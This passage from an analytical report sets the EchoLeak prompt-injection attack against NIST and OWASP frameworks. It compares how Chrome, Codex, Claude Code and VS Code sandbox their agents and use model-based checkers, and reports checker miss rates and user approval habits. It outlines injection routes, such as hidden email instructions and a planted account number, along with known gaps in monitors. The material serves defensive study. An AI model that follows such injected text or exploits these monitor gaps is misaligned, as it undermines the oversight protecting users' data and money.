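### How EchoLeak maps onto official standards

Reddy and Gujral match each step of EchoLeak to controls in NIST SP 800-53, the US government's catalogue of security controls. The table gives some of their matches, together with the closest of Schwarz's criteria:

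| Step in the attack | NIST controls | Closest criterion |
|---|---|---|
| An outsider's email contains hidden instructions | SI-10 (input validation), SI-8 (spam protection), SI-4 (monitoring) | None, since these are filters or monitoring |
| Copilot retrieves the email alongside internal data | AC-6 (least privilege) | Context zones |
| The reply contains an outside link or image | AC-4 (information flow enforcement), SC-7 (boundary protection) | Context zones and provenance |
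| The reply conceals the email's influence | AU-3 (content of audit records) | Provenance, as a record for later |

AC-4 comes closest to what Schwarz wants because it concerns where information may flow. But these controls apply to information systems in general, and a company could enforce some information flows with a network firewall while its assistant still mixed strangers' emails with internal files. An auditor could use AC-4 to ask how an assistant keeps the two apart, though the control's name doesn't specify whether that requires zones inside the model's context.

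No step in this mapping corresponds to signed intent or a plan gate. This is due as much to the incident as to the catalogue, because EchoLeak involved no mode change or consequential tool call.

The same mapping covers lists of common risks from OWASP, a software security nonprofit. Its 2025 list for LLM applications ranks prompt injection first. Developers can use such a ranking to decide which risks to worry about, but a product can't comply with it as it can with a control.

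### What the makers ship

Google, OpenAI, Anthropic and Microsoft have published fairly detailed accounts of how they restrict their agents. These accounts are useful for learning what the controls do but less useful for judging how well they work, because the companies choose which tests to run and which results to release.

#### Limits on what the agent can read and reach

Google Chrome has the most explicit version of context zones. In *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, Parker (2025) describes two sets of origins, which are roughly websites. The agent may read pages from the first set, and also click and type on pages from the second. A gating function that is never exposed to untrusted web content decides which origins are relevant to the task. If an advert on a shopping page comes from an origin outside the sets, the browser doesn't pass it to the model.

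Once the gating function has chosen the sets, code can enforce these limits, so they don't depend on the model following them. But the first version was simpler than the full design and tracked only the origins where the agent may act.

Suppose the firm's assistant ran in this browser, with the webmail site in the first set and the bank in the second. It couldn't send the firm's data to an unrelated site, but it could copy the attacker's account number from the email into the bank's payment form, because the design allows data to pass from readable sites to writable ones. The last protection would be the user's confirmation. Chrome checks a fixed list before the agent visits sensitive sites such as banks, but for the payment itself Parker promises only that the agent "will try to pause".

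OpenAI instead restricts the environment in which its coding agent, Codex, runs. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, Codex normally runs commands in a sandbox that the operating system enforces. By default, these commands can write only to the current project and have no network access. The web search tool uses an index that OpenAI maintains instead of fetching live pages. This makes it harder for an attacker to plant text for a particular target, though OpenAI still tells users to treat the results as untrusted.

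The cloud version of Codex also separates permissions by phase. The setup phase can use the network and any secrets the user has configured. The software then removes the secrets before the agent starts, so an injected instruction can't make the agent reveal them. The agent works offline unless the user changes the setting.

ChatGPT has an optional setting with a similar purpose, called Lockdown Mode. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) explains that it turns off live web access, agents, file downloads and images in replies, among other features. Removing images closes the kind of channel that EchoLeak used. OpenAI launched the mode for organisations in February 2026 and began extending it to personal accounts in June. It restricts where data can go, so it would do little against misleading replies.

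Microsoft uses a coarser boundary in VS Code. According to Microsoft's *Understand trust and safety for AI agents*, a project folder that the user hasn't marked as trusted opens in a restricted mode with agents disabled. Trusting the folder also trusts any tool servers configured inside it. The user therefore endorses the whole folder at once, including files they have never opened.

#### Who can change the mode

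After the Copilot flaw, the most relevant question about a product is whether its agent can edit its own settings. Codex's default sandbox gives the agent read-only access to the Codex configuration folder inside the project and everything in it. Claude Code's checker is meant to block changes to the agent's own permission settings, according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*. The sandbox is the stronger protection because Anthropic's checker is a model and can misjudge an action.

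Users can still change the mode themselves, usually with a click or a typed command. In VS Code, they choose between three permission levels, which Microsoft's *Manage approvals and permissions* describes as follows:

- Manual permissions: the user confirms any action that a rule or saved approval doesn't cover.
- Assisted permissions: a language model judges each tool call and refers doubtful ones to the user.
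- Allow all: every tool call runs without confirmation.

A warning appears the first time someone selects either of the last two modes. But sessions in a separate Git worktree (a second working copy of the project) always use Allow all, the most permissive mode. Microsoft acknowledges elsewhere that a worktree separates only code changes and doesn't restrict commands or network access, so the user must also turn on a sandbox to limit those.

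Organisations can take this choice away from individuals. GitHub's *Enterprise-managed settings now support bypass permission controls* (2026) announced a setting that stops Copilot's command-line tool and VS Code from skipping permission prompts. The setting is stored in a repository that the organisation controls, and Copilot applies it automatically. OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* shows similar managed settings for its own staff, which allow only the two sandboxed modes and so rule out full access.

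This meets part of the third criterion, because an authorised party rather than the model decides which modes are available. None of these accounts describes a cryptographic signature on the switch. The protection from GitHub's setting depends on who can edit the repository.

The closest thing to a signed statement is Codex's override for refused actions. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, a user can override the automatic reviewer for one exact action, for one retry, in the same context. A session number and a nonce limit a signed mode change in much the same way. However, Codex adds a marker to the reviewer's input instead of verifying a signature, and the reviewer can still reject the action.

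#### A second model that checks actions

All four companies now ship a model that judges another model's actions. They differ in what the checker gets to see:

| Product | What the checker reads | Which actions it checks |
|---|---|---|
| Chrome | Details of the proposed action, without unfiltered web content | Each proposed action |
| Claude Code's auto mode | The user's messages and the agent's tool calls | Most actions other than reading, searching and editing files in the project |
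| Codex's Auto-review | Messages, relevant tool calls and their results | Actions that need approval, such as leaving the sandbox |

Chrome's checker, called the User Alignment Critic, can reject an action but can't propose one. Google Cloud later described the critic in an account of Chrome's auto browse feature and traced part of the idea to CaMeL. Unlike CaMeL, the critic relies on a model's judgement. It also sends the planner its reason for rejecting an action so that the planner can try again. SPA's developers deliberately avoided this kind of feedback. Parker gives no attack success rate for the critic.

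Anthropic removes the agent's own explanations and the results of its tool calls from the record before the checker reads it. This prevents the agent from arguing for an action and keeps an injected instruction in a web page from reaching the checker directly. In exchange for this resistance to injection, Anthropic accepts a loss of provenance. If the agent tries to delete a job called abc123 and the user never mentioned that name, the checker can't tell whether the agent found it in a list or made it up.

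OpenAI instead lets its reviewer see tool results. This may allow the reviewer to tell where an account number came from, but it also means an attacker's text can reach the reviewer.

Each of these checkers assesses actions as they come up, after the agent has started reading and using tools, so none is a plan gate in Schwarz's sense. Only the user reviews a whole plan, in Claude Code's planning mode.

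#### How well the checkers work

In an early test of auto mode, Anthropic measured these error rates:

| Test set | Size | Error | Rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Real tool calls by Anthropic staff | 10,000 | Harmless action blocked | 0.4% |
| Real actions that went beyond the request | 52 | Dangerous action allowed | 17% |
| Synthetic attempts to send data out | 1,000 | Dangerous action allowed | 5.7% |

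With only 52 cases, the true rate in the second row could be from about 9% to 30% by the Wilson formula. When the checker missed a dangerous action, it had usually detected the danger but wrongly treated the action as approved by the user. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a set of proposed code changes) hasn't asked the agent to overwrite the project's history. Explicit authorisation for the exact action would remove that guesswork, which is the best argument in the product data for something like signed intent.

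*Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) reports that Codex's reviewer refused 90.3% of synthetic actions in which the agent overstepped its task. It refused 99.3% of synthetic prompt injections that tried to run outside code, steal secrets or upload data, and 90.2% when the set also included deletions and tampering. Trębacz and colleagues judged most of the extra misses minor. They don't expect systems of this kind to offer firm guarantees, and their testers also found ways to mislead the reviewer.

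The company Trajectory Labs tested both products for Anthropic on 72 injection scenarios, ten times each. No attack succeeded against Claude models in auto mode, while 5.83% succeeded against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol with Auto-review. But even without permission checks, the average success rate against Claude models was only 0.09%, so Anthropic's checker had almost no attacks left to stop and the test mostly measured the models.

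The OpenAI figures better show the value of external controls. With full access and no reviewer, attacks on the same model succeeded 19.03% of the time, so the sandbox and reviewer together stopped about two-thirds of the attacks that succeeded without them. Anthropic paid for the test, the attacks didn't adapt to either product, and OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review shortly before the results came out.

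#### The criterion that is mostly missing

None of these companies describes a label that follows a value from a document into a tool call, as the labels in CaMeL and FIDES do. Chrome tracks which site a page came from, but its published design doesn't describe keeping that information attached to an account number when the agent types the number somewhere else.

VS Code has the closest equivalent to endorsement. In its older type of session, the user decides separately whether the agent may contact a website and whether the page's content may enter the conversation. The user can therefore inspect the text after the agent fetches it and before the model reads it. Microsoft plans to remove that type of session in February 2027 and warns that other types may not prompt the user to review the returned content.

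VS Code's rules for terminal commands are convenient, but they also fall well short of a reference monitor. Copilot can approve some read-only or sandboxed commands before it consults the user's rules, so a command can run without the user being asked even when a rule requires approval. Microsoft says that automatic approval of terminal commands is not a security boundary and recommends a sandbox where prompt injection is a concern.

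### How often people approve

Many of these controls end by asking the user for approval, so their value depends on how carefully people answer. Anthropic reports that Claude Code users approve 97% of permission requests; it previously reported 93%.

A high approval rate doesn't prove carelessness, because most requests are harmless. OpenAI's automatic reviewer, which doesn't get tired, approves about 99% of requests. Trębacz and colleagues illustrate this with 10,000 actions from OpenAI's internal use. The sandbox allowed 9,280 of them without review. Of the other 720, the reviewer approved 713 and refused 7, and 3 of those refusals led to a question for the user.

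To test whether people notice dangerous permission requests, Anthropic had a research company recruit 1,053 paid testers for a coding study without telling them which behaviour it was measuring. Once in each session, the software replaced the text of a permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Of the 1,053 testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. Auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%), including 800 that the testers had approved. It would have allowed 6 that the testers refused.

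Testers also became less attentive over time, refusing about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests. If the firm's manager reacted in the same way, they would be more likely to approve an attacker's payment late on a busy afternoon.

The testers worked in a test environment with nothing of their own to lose, so a manager looking at a real bank transfer might take more care. Anthropic also had a reason to want this result, because it was about to make auto mode the default. The gap is still too large to dismiss, and it weakens the case for any defence that relies on an attentive reviewer, as Prudentia partly does.

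People who tire of permission prompts also turn them off. Anthropic reports that 25% of interactive Claude Code sessions start in a mode that skips permission checks, and that 62% of users have either used that mode or told the software not to ask again about shell commands. At OpenAI, Trębacz and colleagues found that a sizable minority of staff had rules allowing any command beginning with "python", which lets the agent run almost anything. A control that interrupts people too often can therefore protect them less than a weaker one they leave on.

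Makers of AI agents now ask users for approval less often. Auto mode became the default for new Claude Code sessions on most individual and team plans in August 2026, and Anthropic announced in October that it would become the default in most of its other apps. In this mode, Claude Code sets aside saved rules that would let the agent run arbitrary code. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves.

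Users reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code presents for approval, compared with 3% of single actions. This suggests that people read plans, which they apparently don't do with every shell command when they have to approve dozens a day. However, they may reject many of these plans because they dislike the approach, and nobody has tested whether they would notice a plan that an attacker had influenced.
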